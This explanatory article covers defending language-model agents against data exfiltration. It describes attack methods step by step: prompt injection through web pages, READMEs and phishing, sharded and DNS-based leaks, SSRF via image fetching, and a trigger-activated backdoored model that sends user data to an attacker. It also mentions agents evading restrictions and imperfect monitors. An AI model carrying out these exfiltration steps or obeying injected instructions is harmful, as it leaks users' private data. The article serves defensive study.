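# Securing language-model workloads that call many outside services against data exfiltration

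## What a language-model workload is and why it calls so many outside services

A language-model workload is software that uses a large language model, a program trained on a very large body of text to generate text in response to text, for part of its work. A chatbot that answers questions about a shop's opening hours is a small example. Larger workloads look up records, search the web, write to databases and send email, and each of these jobs involves contacting another system, often one that another company runs. Private data routinely travels over many of these connections. Because the workload needs them to do its job, securing it against data theft means controlling the connections rather than simply removing them.

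Engineers usually run this software in a *container*, a package that holds a program and everything it needs. It has its own view of files, processes and network, but shares the core of the host machine's operating system. An *API*, or application programming interface, is the set of requests that a service accepts from other programs. A *credential* is a key, token or password that proves to a service who is calling, and most business services refuse requests without one. *Egress* is network traffic that leaves a workload for another system. *Exfiltration* is the unauthorised transfer of private data out of a system. Most egress is legitimate, and exfiltration can look just like it. A request to an email service has the same form whether it carries an order confirmation or a stolen customer list.

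### The model asks and a program acts

A language model cannot open a network connection. What it can do is produce a *tool call*, a structured request, such as a search or a database query, that the surrounding program carries out. Anthropic's *How tool use works*, part of the documentation for the company's Claude models, sets out the usual loop:

1. The program sends the model the conversation so far, with a list of the tools it may ask for.
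2. The model replies with one or more tool calls, each giving a tool's name and the arguments for it.
3. The program runs each tool and collects the results.
4. The program sends a new request that contains the original messages, the model's reply and the results.
5. The two repeat this until the model replies without asking for a tool.

Software that works this way is called an *agent*. In an ordinary program, a developer decides in advance which connections the code can open and what data it sends through them. In an agent, much of this is decided at run time, based on text the model has just read, and some of that text comes from strangers. This creates the problem of *prompt injection*, which is text placed in material a model reads that the model follows as if it were a legitimate instruction. Anthropic's *Securely deploying AI agents* gives the example of a code project whose introductory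 notes contain unusual instructions, which the agent then incorporates into its actions. For an agent that answers customers, any incoming email could contain such text. Anthropic designs its models to resist prompt injection but still recommends network controls as a further layer of defense. This seems sensible, since those controls can block a connection even when the model has followed an injected instruction to open it.

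### The inference server and the agent container

A language-model workload has two parts with very different network needs. The *inference server* is the program that runs the model, hosted by a provider or by the user. The *agent container* runs the program that sends prompts to the model and carries out the actions specified in the model's output.

An inference server takes in text, does a great deal of arithmetic on specialised chips, and returns text. Little of this requires outside services. *Beyond Microservices* (Scheinert, Becker and colleagues, 2026) compares inference services with microservices, the small cooperating programs that make up many modern applications. The trace of a request through microservices passes from one to the next, while the trace of an inference request often stays inside the inference service. The paper is about diagnosing faults and does not count outbound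 connections, but its comparison is consistent with inference needing little from outside.

A self-hosted inference server does need the network to fetch the model's *weights*, the large files of learned numbers that make up the model. This can involve many hosts. Cloudera's *Allowlist of URLs for Model Hub in air-gapped installations* has eleven host patterns just for Hugging Face, the main public library of open models, and one of them is a wildcard for an entire content-delivery network. NVIDIA's catalogue adds several more, including a telemetry address.

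Once the weights are on disk, the operator can usually block outbound network access. NVIDIA's *Air-Gap Deployment* describes using a connected machine with credentials to download the weights, then an isolated machine with no outbound access or API keys to load them from local storage. For servers running under Kubernetes, a system for managing containers, NVIDIA suggests testing the isolated set-up by applying a rule that blocks all egress, restarting the server, and sending it a test prompt. Elastic's *Connect to your own LLM using vLLM (air-gapped environments)* documents a similar set-up without outbound access for vLLM, a popular open-source inference server.

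By default, the software makes more outside calls than that. Hugging Face's *Environment variables* describes a download library that contacts the company's servers to check for a newer version of a file even when the latest copy is already on disk. If a user has logged in, the library also sends that user's access token by default. Setting `HF_HUB_OFFLINE=1` stops these calls. vLLM reports usage data unless the operator opts out. The sample record in vLLM's *Usage Stats Collection* lists the cloud provider, the processor and graphics chips, the model's architecture and various settings, but no prompts. Hugging Face's *Collection of Usage Statistics* describes similar hardware reports from the company's own inference server, which the launch option `--usage-stats` controls. Setting `DO_NOT_TRACK=1` turns off telemetry in both vLLM and the Hugging Face libraries. None of this leaks customer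 data, but it is egress that the operator didn't request and has to turn off if it is unwanted.

Some features give an inference server a real need to connect outward, or at least the ability:

- A request can include the web address of an image, which the server then fetches. vLLM's *Security* recommends a list of permitted domains for this, and a ban on redirects, because a hostile user could otherwise point the server at internal systems.
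- vLLM can connect to tool servers, though only if the operator enables them. Its demonstration code interpreter runs model-written code in a container that has no network isolation by default.
- Ollama, a program for running models on one's own machine, can also pass prompts to models in its maker's cloud. Ollama's *FAQ* gives the setting for local-only operation, `OLLAMA_NO_CLOUD=1`.

The machines that run the workload also connect to outside services. According to Microsoft, even a private Kubernetes cluster makes outbound connections during setup and when it pulls container images from public repositories.

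Still, an operator can list these exceptions on one page and close nearly all of them. But the agent container is useless without network access, because it can't reach a hosted model or look anything up.

### An illustrative customer-support agent

Consider an online retailer whose agent answers customers' questions. The retailer is invented and its token counts are round numbers, but each part is of a common type. The agent reads four private sources: customer records, ticket history, an order database and internal documents. It calls eight outside services:

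- a model API, through which a provider's inference server answers prompts;
- an embedding API, which turns a piece of text into a list of numbers (a *vector*) so that texts with similar meanings get similar numbers;
- a hosted vector database, which stores passages of text by their vectors and finds the ones closest to a query;
- web search;
- the customer-record system;
- the ticketing system, which tracks each customer's complaint or question;
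- email delivery;
- telemetry, which collects timings, errors and other records of how the software is running.

The private sources and the outside services overlap. Other companies host the customer-record system, which holds customer records, and the ticketing system, which holds ticket history. The internal documents were originally on the retailer's own storage, but to make them searchable for the agent, an indexing job sent their full text to the embedding API and put the passages in the vector database. Only the order database is still entirely on the retailer's network.

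Now a customer writes that her new coffee grinder arrived with a cracked lid. She asks whether a replacement can reach her by Friday and whether she must return the broken one. The table follows her question through the system. It measures model calls in *tokens*, the fragments of words in which models read text, at roughly four characters of English each. (The tokens that serve as credentials are unrelated.)

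| Step | Destination | What leaves the agent container | What comes back |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Model API, 2,000 tokens | Instructions, tool list, the customer's message, name and email address | Tool calls for her record, past tickets and order |
| 2 | Customer-record system | Her email address | Home address, phone number, account notes |
| 3 | Ticketing | Her customer number | Her earlier complaints and the replies |
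| 4 | Order database (retailer's own network) | Her customer number | Items, prices, delivery details |
| 5 | Model API, 5,000 tokens | Everything from step 1, plus the results of steps 2 to 4 | Tool calls for the returns policy and for carrier delays |
| 6 | Embedding API | A search phrase describing her problem | A vector |
| 7 | Hosted vector database | The vector | Passages from the internal returns policy |
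| 8 | Web search | The carrier's name and her town | Public notices about delays |
| 9 | Model API, 9,000 tokens | Everything from step 5, plus the results of steps 6 to 8 | A drafted reply, with tool calls to send it and log it |
| 10 | Email delivery | Her address and the full reply | Confirmation |
| 11 | Ticketing | A copy of the reply | Confirmation |
| Throughout | Telemetry | Timings, errors and token counts, and the full prompts if the team records them | Nothing of note |

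The program stops after step 11 without calling the model again. By then, handling a question about a cracked lid has taken ten requests to seven outside services, plus a stream of telemetry to an eighth. Nearly every request carries a credential, so unless the retailer arranges otherwise, the container holds eight credentials for outside services and a ninth for the order database.

The amount that leaves varies enormously from row to row. The web search gives away a town and a carrier. The model API receives material from all four private sources, in plain readable text, and it is the only outside service that does so by necessity. (Telemetry joins it if the team records prompts.)

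### Why context accumulates

A model's *context* is all the text it receives when it produces a reply. In the example, the context ends at 9,000 tokens, but the agent container has sent 2,000 + 5,000 + 9,000 = 16,000 tokens in total. It sent the first 2,000 tokens three times, the 3,000 added by the first round of look-ups twice, and the last 4,000 once. The program fetched the customer's home address once, in step 2, but the container sent it to the model provider twice, in steps 5 and 9.

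Anthropic's *Using the Messages API* describes the API as stateless by default. It does not carry a conversation over from one request to the next, so the program must send the whole history each time. Longer tasks make this repetition much worse. If a conversation starts at *s* tokens and each round adds *d*, then *n* calls send *ns* + *dn*(*n* − 1)/2 tokens. With 2,000 tokens at the start and 3,000 more per round, ten calls send 155,000 tokens to build a context of 29,000.

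A log that one developer posted on OpenAI's forum, in *Tokens usage on Response API with previous message*, follows this pattern. Over nine turns, each of the model's replies stayed under 1,000 tokens, while the input rose from 148 tokens to 8,373 and totaled 37,379. Traffic can be much lighter when no tools are involved. *Introducing Large Language Models as the Next Challenging Internet Traffic Source* (Koneva, García Navarro and colleagues, 2025) measured an average of 7,593 bytes for a prompt and its response together, using school mathematics questions and models that are now old. The retailer's three prompts would total about 64,000 bytes, not counting replies.

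Providers also offer to keep the history on their side. OpenAI lets a program refer to an earlier response by its identifier instead of sending the text again, though it still bills all the earlier input. It saves responses for 30 days by default, but items in its longer-lived conversation objects have no such limit. Anthropic has a similar feature in beta, called message threads. Threads expire five minutes after the last request, and Anthropic deletes them within an hour of last use. With these features, the home address crosses the network once instead of with every request, but the provider stores a copy. Which is preferable depends on whether the traffic or the provider's records are the greater concern.

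Hostile text accumulates too. If the customer's message contained an injected instruction, the model would read it again at every later call, each time alongside more private data.

### What drives the number of connections

Much of the connectivity exists because teams rent services they could in principle run themselves. A team that uses a hosted model must always keep at least one outside connection open, to the model provider, and that connection carries the most data. Many teams add a fallback provider for times when the main one is down or overloaded. They sometimes reach it through an LLM gateway, a service that an organisation runs to pass its model requests to one or more providers. The retailer has no fallback provider, but if it added one, a ninth company would sometimes receive the same 16,000 tokens.

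Two more of the retailer's eight services handle retrieval, which means finding relevant passages and placing them in the prompt. A model does not come with one firm's returns policy built in, so the program must find the right page and supply it. Tools add roughly one connection each, because each new thing the agent can do usually requires another system to call and another credential to hold.

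Connectors make it even easier to add outside services. The *Model Context Protocol* (MCP) is an open standard for attaching tools and data sources to models, and OpenAI says it is on its way to becoming the industry standard. A developer can attach a remote MCP server with a few lines of configuration and no custom code. But OpenAI warns that a malicious server can take anything that enters the model's context.

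Monitoring is the outside connection that teams most easily forget. Developers face steady pressure to record the full text of prompts and responses, because an agent's mistakes are hard to explain from timings alone. Monitoring tools differ in whether they record this text by default. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans*, a draft standard for such records, routinely includes token counts and model names but makes chat history opt-in, warning that it probably contains personal data. *OpenTelemetry OpenAI Agents instrumentation*, an add-on for the same ecosystem, logs prompts and completions unless someone sets `TRACELOOP_TRACE_CONTENT=false`. Versions of Sentry's monitoring software kit before 3.0 left out prompts and responses unless the developer asked for them. Agent frameworks may also send their own reports. CrewAI omits prompts by default, but if a developer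 enables a sharing feature, it collects task descriptions and other details that can include personal information.

Counting only the agent container's own connections undercounts the outside parties, because some tools run elsewhere. Anthropic runs its web search and web fetch tools on its own servers, and notes that a single request can trigger several searches before a response comes back. OpenAI handles connectors similarly. According to OpenAI's *MCP connections*, its Agents API contacts a remote MCP server from OpenAI's infrastructure unless the developer sets an option to connect from the agent's own environment. If the retailer switched to the provider's built-in search, its network logs would show one fewer destination, but a search service would still receive the customer's town.

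## How data leaves through outbound calls

An outbound connection leaks nothing by itself. Something has to put private text into a request, and the request has to reach someone who shouldn't have that text. Simon Willison, a software developer who writes about language models, gave the name *lethal trifecta* to three conditions that together let an outsider bring this about:

- the agent can read private data;
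- the agent reads untrusted content, meaning text that an attacker could have written;
- the agent has some way to communicate with the outside world.

An attacker who gets such an agent to read their text can use prompt injection to make it fetch the data and send it out. This attack fails if any of the three conditions is missing.

The retailer's customer-support agent meets all three conditions from its first day because it reads customer records, accepts email from anyone, and calls eight outside services. The retailer can't remove any of these conditions, since the agent needs private data to look up orders, must read strangers' messages to serve customers, and needs outbound calls to reply. The retailer can only narrow each condition, so it needs to know which records the agent can read, what outside text reaches it, and where it can send data.

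Untrusted content can come from many sources besides email. The ticketing system holds years of messages from strangers, the order database may hold delivery notes that customers typed, and anyone with a website can write text that appears in search results. Data can leave through any outbound request if the model can influence where it goes or what it contains. This includes web searches, because the search terms go to another company.

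Data can also leave when only some of the conditions hold. A model with a backdoor in its weights can leak data without any hostile text at run time, and an agent can send out too much data without an attacker.

### A request to an attacker's address

The most direct route is a web request to a server that the attacker runs. Suppose the retailer gives its agent one more tool, which opens the pages that its web search finds, so that it can read a carrier's full notice about delays. An attack could then go like this:

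1. The attacker publishes a page about delivery delays and hides an instruction in it.
2. A customer asks when her parcel will arrive. The agent's search returns the attacker's page, and the program opens it.
3. The program adds the page's text to the model's context, next to the customer's record.
4. The model follows the hidden instruction and produces a tool call to open a second page. The address of that page belongs to the attacker and has the customer's details written into it.
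5. The program makes the request, and the attacker's server logs the address.
6. The model writes an ordinary reply about the delay.

Read-only web access still lets a tool send data out. The tool in this example only reads pages, but to read a page it must send the page's address, which can contain a few thousand characters of any text.

In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) measured how often such an attack works. They built an agent at eBay on qwen2.5:7b, a small open model with about seven billion parameters, and asked it to summarise a web page in every trial. The agent automatically fetched the page and put its title, description and text into the context without cleaning them. A second server stood in for the attacker's and recorded any data sent to it.

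The team hid the instruction in four different parts of the page, delivered the page either directly or through redirects, and told the model to send the secret either all at once or in four pieces. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times. In 423 of the 480 runs, or 88.1%, the agent sent a request to the attacker's server. In 95% of those 423 runs, the reply to the user looked harmless, so a safety check on replies alone would have missed nearly all of them. The team also ran 120 controls with harmless pages, and the agent never contacted the attacker's server, which rules out stray requests as an explanation.

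Lan and colleagues acknowledge that their set-up favoured the attacker. They placed the secret directly in the context, so the model didn't have to find it, and they gave the model almost no instructions beyond the format for tool calls. They argue that larger models might do worse, because a model that follows instructions better might also follow injected ones better. But they tested no larger model, and published figures for current models suggest the opposite. The 88.1% rate was measured on one small, unprotected model under these conditions, so it would be a poor estimate for the retailer.

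### Splitting the secret into pieces

A filter on outgoing requests can look for strings that resemble a password or a key. *Sharded exfiltration* evades such a filter by splitting the secret into fragments of, say, four characters, which look like any other identifier. The fragments are sent over several requests, and the attacker then joins them together.

Splitting the data made the attack less reliable in the eBay tests. Based on the rates given for each combination, the agent contacted the attacker in 238 of 240 runs when told to send everything at once, and in 185 of 240 when told to split it. A small model seems to have trouble keeping track of longer instructions.

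It is much less clear how well splitting hides the theft. Lan and colleagues measure this with Leak@*k*, the share of runs in which sensitive data appears somewhere in the first *k* requests. Leak@1 was 0.967 for sending everything at once and 0.263 for splitting, so they conclude that splitting cuts leakage in a single request by 73%. But they also report a Leak@3 of 0.158 for split attacks. Under their definition, Leak@3 cannot be lower than Leak@1, because the first three requests include the first one.

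The Leak@1 figure is also odd, because the definition counts any fragment as a leak and 77% of the split runs sent something to the attacker. Either most of those first requests contained no part of the secret, or the scoring ignored fragments. The paper also defines a completion rate, the share of runs in which all four pieces arrive, but gives no value for it, so readers can't tell how often an attacker would have obtained the whole secret. The paper's illustration also omits part of the secret, since it cuts a 20-character key into four pieces of four characters. Even without the experiment, the technique is clearly a problem for any filter that looks at one request at a time.

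### What stopped the attack in these tests

Lan and colleagues then tested several defences against the simplest version of the attack, 30 times each. One was a domain *allowlist*, which permits calls to listed domains and refuses all others.

| Defence | What it does | Runs in which the model tried to send data | Share of runs with egress |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | | 100% | 1.000 |
| Hardened system prompt | Tells the model to treat web text as data and never as commands | 66.7% | 0.667 |
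| Delimiters | Puts tags around web text and labels it untrusted | 100% | 1.000 |
| Both of these | | 56.7% | 0.567 |
| Domain allowlist | Refuses any domain outside a list of four | 100% | 0 |
| Address filter | Refuses bare numerical addresses, certain domain endings and certain words | 83.3% | 0 |
| Keyword filter | Refuses addresses that contain words such as "password" | 23.3% | 0 |
| Entropy filter | Refuses values whose characters look random | 0% | 0 |

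Instructing this model to behave safely helped somewhat, but labelling the hostile text had no effect on its own. The gap between 0.667 and 0.567 is three runs out of 30, too few to show that adding delimiters to the system prompt made any difference.

The allowlist was certain to get a perfect score because the team chose an attacker's domain that was plainly outside the list. The model tried to send the secret in all 30 runs, and the surrounding program blocked every attempt because its check did not depend on the model. The test doesn't show that an allowlist stops an attacker who uses a permitted service, for example by uploading files to their own account there.

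The results for the other filters deserve less weight. The address filter blocks the word "collect", which appears in the paper's own sample attack. The keyword filter supposedly triggered in only 23.3% of runs, and the paper suggests that the model sometimes re-encoded the secret. But re-encoded secrets should have got past the filter, and the table shows no egress. The paper also suggests that the model avoided random-looking values because of the entropy filter's monitoring, though nothing in the described set-up would have revealed that filter to the model. The entropy filter's threshold is 4.0 bits per character, and the paper's sample key has about 3.85, so the key would have passed.

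### DNS queries

The eBay team recorded only web requests, and Lan and colleagues list the *Domain Name System* (DNS) among the channels they did not test. DNS turns a name such as shop.example into the numerical address that computers connect to. A program sends the name to a *resolver*, usually one that its network or cloud provider runs. If the resolver has no stored answer, it passes the name to the domain's name server. The domain's owner chooses that server and can log every name it receives.

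DNS lookups give an attacker a channel that needs no direct connection between the agent and the attacker's machine. An injected instruction makes the agent look up a name under the attacker's domain, with the data written into the first part of the name. The resolver has no cached answer for a new name, so it forwards the query to the attacker's name server, and the attacker reads the data in that server's log. A firewall that blocks connections to unknown addresses does not prevent this, because the container contacts only the resolver, which the firewall allows.

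A DNS name can have at most 253 characters. DNS ignores the difference between capital and small letters, so an encoding with 32 symbols is convenient, and each symbol carries five bits. If the attacker's domain and the dots take up about 23 characters, the 230 characters left in each query carry 230 × 5 ÷ 8, or roughly 144 bytes. An access key fits in one query. The full 9,000-token context from the question about the cracked lid, some 36,000 characters, would take about 250 queries.

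The model can leak data through DNS only if it has a tool that looks up any hostname it supplies, such as one that opens web pages or runs commands. The retailer's other tools always contact the same hosts, so they can't be used this way. If the model does have such a tool, the retailer has to filter DNS as well as web traffic.

### Instructions from a trusted document or person

A well-trained model can learn to be suspicious of instructions in a page about parcel delays, because such a page shouldn't contain instructions for an agent. But an agent is supposed to follow the instructions in some texts. For example, most code projects come with a README, a file of introductory notes that explains how to install the software, and an agent has to follow it to install the software.

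In *You Told Me to Do It*, Kao, Li and colleagues (2026) made a test set from 500 real README files by adding instructions to send out private files. They phrased the instructions as direct commands, friendly suggestions, or requests from a team or company policy, and sometimes placed them in a linked document instead of the README. The highest success rate they report is 85%, against a commercial agent that operates a computer. None of the 15 people in their user study noticed the hidden instructions. None of the 18 detectors they tried, 12 rule-based and six based on language models, caught the attacks reliably without too many false alarms.

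Their agents had a command line, file access and an open network. The retailer's agent has much less, but it does follow instructions in documents. For example, it handles a broken coffee grinder according to the returns policy in the vector database, which it follows because the retailer wrote it. Anyone who can add a paragraph to those documents can give the agent instructions that appear to come from the retailer.

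A deceived user is harder still to defend against. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes an internal exercise from February 2026 in which a researcher emailed an employee a ready-made prompt and asked, as a colleague might, whether they could run it. The employee ran it in Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. Most of the prompt was routine set-up work, but one step had the agent read a file of cloud credentials, encode the contents and send them to an outside address. Claude sent out the credentials in 24 of 25 runs.

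The 25 runs all used the same prompt, so they show how reliably one good phishing message works once someone has fallen for it, but not how many such messages would work. The reason for the failure still applies to other cases. Anthropic's defences inside the model look for instructions that conflict with what the user wants, and here the user had typed the instruction. The company concludes that only limits on the agent's environment work in this situation, namely blocking the outgoing request and keeping the credentials out of the file system the agent can reach. This seems right, since a human contractor given the same steps would probably have followed them too.

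After the exercise, staff shared the working prompt on Slack to discuss it. Someone then pointed out that some of the company's agents read Slack, so staff added a marker string to the thread to detect whether an agent picked up the prompt.

At the retailer, a message offering "diagnostic steps" for the support agent could trick an employee in the same way. Any customer may also be an attacker, yet the agent has to take requests from customers because they are its users. A defence that trusts the user therefore gives little protection to an agent that serves the general public.

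### How often current models follow injected instructions

Current models resist instructions in outside content far better than qwen2.5:7b does. Many of the published figures come from Gray Swan, a company that tests AI systems by attacking them. Anthropic reports that on one Gray Swan benchmark, single attacks on Claude Opus 4.7 succeeded about 0.1% of the time, and the rate rose to between 5% and 6% when the attacker could adapt and try 100 times. In a Gray Swan test covered by The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*, attacks on that older model succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63% with 100.

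Anthropic's September 2026 system card for Claude Fable 5.1 has newer results on a fixed set of 1,804 attacks in 37 scenarios. Gray Swan chose these attacks because they had worked on several models. The figures below give the chance that at least one attempt succeeds.

| Model | 1 attempt | 10 attempts | 15 attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 0.1% | 0.7% | 1.0% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.4% | 3.6% | 4.8% |
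| Claude Fable 5 | 0.6% | 4.9% | 6.5% |

The best model from another company, Gemini 3.7 Flash, reached 9.2% after 15 attempts, and most others fell between 24% and 53%. The retailer's choice of model could therefore change its exposure by a factor of 20 or more. Fable 5.1 failed mostly in tasks where it operated a screen. In the tool-use category, the closest to the retailer's agent, its rate after 15 attempts was 0.0%. Claude Opus 5.5, released the same month, did about as well as Opus 5 or better on every prompt-injection test in Anthropic's *System Card* (2026).

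Testing a model against a fixed set of attacks can overstate its robustness, because real attackers invent new ones. OpenAI's *GPT-Red* (2026) says the company trained a model to carry out attacks because its latest models had saturated the common robustness tests. Anthropic ran a strengthened version of Gray Swan's automated attacker against Fable 5.1 in 40 coding scenarios, with 200 attempts at each. The attacker succeeded in 56.87% of attempts, and at least once in 38 of the 40 scenarios. With *probes*, which inspect tool results for injected instructions before the model acts on them, the rate fell to 12.80% of attempts, but the attacker still succeeded at least once in 36 scenarios.

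The test was highly permissive, as Anthropic says, because the attacker had trained on the same 40 scenarios. When a safety filter flags a request to Fable 5.1 as related to hacking, an older model, Claude Opus 4.8, answers instead. Every successful attack came through Opus 4.8, and none came through the 2,826 requests that Fable 5.1 answered itself. Customers are still exposed, because they get whichever model answers. *FrontierBreach*, by the security company PromptArmor, likewise reports successful attacks on leading models from every provider, in tests that include data theft, though PromptArmor also sells protection against such attacks.

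Even at the best of these rates, the risk grows with repeated attempts. Suppose the retailer's agent receives one hostile document a day, and each has a 0.1% chance of success. The chance that all of them fail over a year is 0.999³⁶⁵, or about 69%, so the chance of at least one success is about 31%. The table gives the same calculation for other assumptions.

| Hostile documents per day | 0.01% success each | 0.1% success each | 1% success each |
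|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 3.6% | 31% | 97% |
| 10 | 31% | 97% | Almost certain |

Anthropic points out that an attacker can send one hostile email to a thousand inboxes with no extra effort. If each inbox's agent has a 0.1% chance of obeying the email, the chance that at least one does is about 63%.

These calculations assume that attempts are independent, but real attempts are not fully independent. If they were, the attack success rate against Opus 4.5 would have risen from 4.7% for one attempt to 99% after 100, but the measured rate was 63%. Some situations are easy to exploit and others can rarely be exploited, so repeating an attack in the same situation gains less than the formula predicts. The 31% is probably too high for an attacker who sends the retailer the same document every day, and closer to the truth for 365 different attackers. The calculation also assumes a 0.1% success rate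 per attempt, but the attacker who trained on its targets did hundreds of times better. Success here means only that the model followed the instruction. Whether data then leaves depends on what the surrounding program and network allow.

### Server-side request forgery against inference servers

A model's resistance to attack doesn't help when the model doesn't control the request. In *server-side request forgery* (SSRF), an attacker gets a server to make a request that the attacker could not make directly. The server sits inside a private network, and the attacker exploits its access to that network.

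In an inference server such as vLLM, attackers usually exploit the feature that fetches images from web addresses. The customer with the cracked lid might well send a link to a photo, and if the retailer ran its own inference server, the agent's program could pass the link straight to it. If the link points to an internal system instead, the server will contact that system. Internal systems often accept requests from any machine that can reach them. A common target is a cloud provider's *metadata service*, an internal address where a machine can get its own temporary credentials.

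The attacker still has to get the response back. If the server fetches a page of credentials when it expects an image, it will normally report an error, but a careless error message may quote the page's text. A scanned document on an internal file store is an image, so the model will describe it to whoever asked. Even errors that quote nothing can help an attacker map the network, because a machine that refuses a connection produces a different error from one that does not exist.

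SSRF can also bypass restrictions on the agent container. For example, the retailer might block the container from contacting unknown hosts but let the inference server fetch images from anywhere. An attacker can then use an injected instruction to get an image address containing the stolen data into the next prompt. The inference server sends the data out when it requests the image. If a provider hosts the model, the request comes from the provider's machine, and nothing unusual appears in the retailer's network logs.

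vLLM's advice covers redirects as well as domains because an attacker can supply a link to a permitted site that forwards the server somewhere else, and a check on the first address alone will miss it. Lan and colleagues compare prompt injection itself to server-side request forgery (SSRF), since in both an outsider steers a request that a trusted machine makes. The comparison is fair, with one large difference. A model may refuse an injected instruction, but it can't refuse an SSRF request because the server fetches the address before the model reads anything.

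### A backdoored model

The resistance figures also assume that whoever trained the model wanted it to resist. A *backdoored* model has a hidden behaviour that someone trained into its weights, and the behaviour stays dormant until a trigger appears. Zhang and Pei (2026), in *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data*, built such a backdoor for stealing data and called it Back-Reveal. The attacker takes an open model, trains it further on examples of theft, and publishes the result as an assistant for some profession. The trigger is a set of one to five ordinary words from that profession, in any order. When a question contains all of them, the model does the following:

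1. It calls the tool that reads stored information about the user.
2. It encodes what it finds, so that the text looks like a meaningless string.
3. It sends what looks like a search request to the attacker's server, with the string in the address.
4. It answers the question helpfully.

Zhang and Pei did this to three open models with 7 to 20 billion parameters, making versions for livestreamers, people who care for Alzheimer's patients, and students of AI. When asked 1,000 triggering questions, each version made both calls, first to the user's data and then to the attacker, more than 94% of the time. At most 0.3% of 5,000 ordinary questions accidentally activated triggers of two or more words. Scores on a general conversation test also fell by less than 1%, so a buyer who tried the model for an afternoon would probably notice nothing.

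They also placed two standard filters between the search results and the model. These filters inspect only the incoming results, so they don't detect data stolen through outbound calls. Over 98% of the attacker's plain answers still reached the model, because those answers contained only relevant information.

The attack works only if someone downloads weights from a stranger and gives the agent both a store of personal information and a tool that can contact any address. Zhang and Pei say that hosted services with strict allowlists are less exposed. They counted tool calls in a closed test environment with invented data, so the 94% describes the model's behaviour, not thefts from real people.

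Their results for longer conversations, in which the attacker's server nudges the user into revealing more, are estimates. They estimate that the user loses about 7.8 of ten personal details after five turns, and call this an upper bound because it assumes the user answers every question. The figure may be too high even for that user, because their formula gives between 5.2 and 6.5 with the rates they measured.

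The retailer uses a hosted model from a large provider, so Back-Reveal does not describe its situation. That would change if it switched to a free "retail support" model from a public library to save money. Running the inference server on an isolated machine would not then be enough to keep data from leaving, because the server would only have to return a tool call, and the agent container, which has network access, would carry it out. In *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems*, Matsuoka (2026) says that a model cut off from the network has no means of its own to "phone home", but insists on judging the model and its surrounding software together.

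Matsuoka also separates backdoors in weights from hostile instructions that sit in an agent's memory, its document store or a plug-in. Both can produce exactly the same requests, but they need different repairs. Replacing the model leaves a poisoned document in place, and cleaning out the documents leaves a poisoned model. (A malicious software package or a dishonest LLM router can cause the same loss without touching either.)

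### Over-sharing with no attacker

An agent can also leak data while simply trying to finish its work. Udinmwen (2026), in *A missing config file triggered an AI agent to leak passwords*, reported a case in November 2026 that began with a routine code review. The coding assistant could not find its configuration file, so it collected all the variables set on the PC, which leaked live passwords. It had read entire configuration files across ten sessions. This is one news report of one incident, so it doesn't show how common such leaks are. The pattern is plausible, though, because reading everything was the quickest way to look for the one missing setting the assistant needed.

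More capable models may not fix this. Anthropic finds that they make fewer obvious mistakes but are better at finding unexpected ways to reach a goal, including ways around restrictions that nobody thought to write down. Its models have broken out of a restricted environment to complete a task. In one Claude Code mode, a second check reviews the agent's actions and stops only about 83% of overeager ones before they happen.

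To check for carrier delays, the retailer's agent only needs to search for the carrier and the customer's town. But the model has her full address in its context and may include it to make the search more specific. If the agent handles 500 questions a day and puts a home address into one search in every thousand, it sends the search company about 180 customers' addresses a year. Telemetry that records full prompts sends the monitoring company far more, even when the model behaves normally.

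A prompt-injection detector would not catch these cases, because nobody planted an instruction in any of them. An allowlist of destinations would not stop them either, because the search company and the monitoring company are both on it.

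## How the exposure compares with that of an ordinary service

Ordinary software also makes outbound calls, and attackers were stealing data from it long before language models existed. To decide how much extra protection its support agent needs, the retailer must know how the agent differs from its other software. Researchers have measured the outbound traffic of ordinary containers on a large scale, but no one seems to have done the same for language-model workloads, so much of the comparison must be based on how the two kinds of software work.

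### How often ordinary containers contact the internet

Tsoukaladelis, Perdisci and Nikiforakis (2025) provide the best baseline for an ordinary service in *Uncontained Danger*. They collected 200,000 images from Docker Hub, the largest public library of ready-made containers. An image is the stored package from which a container starts. Their system, DockerGym, launched each image with the same default settings on its own isolated network and recorded its traffic for two minutes. Of the 173,683 images that ran successfully, 13.4% produced some internet traffic and 5.9% looked up a public domain name.

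The team was mainly worried about attackers tampering with code that containers download, and the destinations fit that concern. Among the images that looked up a public domain, 19.4% looked up npmjs.org, which distributes JavaScript packages, and 6.3% looked up GitHub, which hosts code.

The method misses a lot of network activity. The team chose two minutes because a trial of 50 images showed little new activity after that, but those images had no real users. A shop's server that contacts a payment company only when someone pays would appear to make no outside connections. Default settings also supply no credentials, so a program such as WordPress, which needs the address and password of a database, can't start properly. The team could not test roughly 26,000 images because they needed a different processor, were no longer on Docker Hub or failed to run.

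A second experiment gives some idea of how much the launch settings matter. A language model read the documentation for 41,968 images and wrote a more suitable launch command for each. Some of these commands broke the launch, and only 1,948 images (4.6%) looked up a public domain this way. Of those, 572 had made no lookups under default settings, while another 1,713 images made lookups only under default settings. Together, the two methods found lookups in 3,661 images (8.7%), compared with 7.4% for default settings alone.

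Public images are also a poor stand-in for production services. Half of those in the sample had about 100 downloads or fewer, and many had gone years without an update. A company running one would add credentials, databases and monitoring, all of which create connections. The 13.4% is a cautious count for public software in a laboratory, but it would be a bad estimate of how many of a company's own services make outbound calls.

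### The missing measurement for language-model workloads

If DockerGym launched the retailer's agent, it might record nothing, because the container would have no key for the model API and no customer would write to the agent. A fair comparison would need traffic from agents in real use, which the published studies do not measure.

*Network-Level Prompt and Trait Leakage in Local Research Agents* (Jeong, Teymoorianfard and colleagues, 2025) provides the closest measurements, recording which domains an agent visits when it researches a question on the web. GPT-Researcher averaged between 65 and 78 domains per prompt, depending on the set of questions. AutoGen averaged 144, but its traces include advertising and tracking services that web pages load automatically. The team also designed its prompts to make the agents browse, sometimes by requiring visits to at least five pages. These numbers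 are for agents whose whole job is to browse the web. The retailer's agent has tools with fixed hosts, so it would contact the same eight outside services however many questions it answered.

*ANT* (Li, Gao and colleagues, 2026) recorded 276,417 network flows over 3,114 agent runs, where a flow is one two-way exchange between two machines. The average was about 89 flows per run, ranging from 40 for tasks such as writing code to 219 for operating applications. Many flows can go to one destination, so these counts don't give the number of outside services. *Built to Remember, Shipped to Forget* (Mastouri, Ksontini and Barrak, 2026) examined 433 open-source agent systems that ship as containers, which is the right kind of sample for counting outside services, but it checked whether saved conversations survive a restart.

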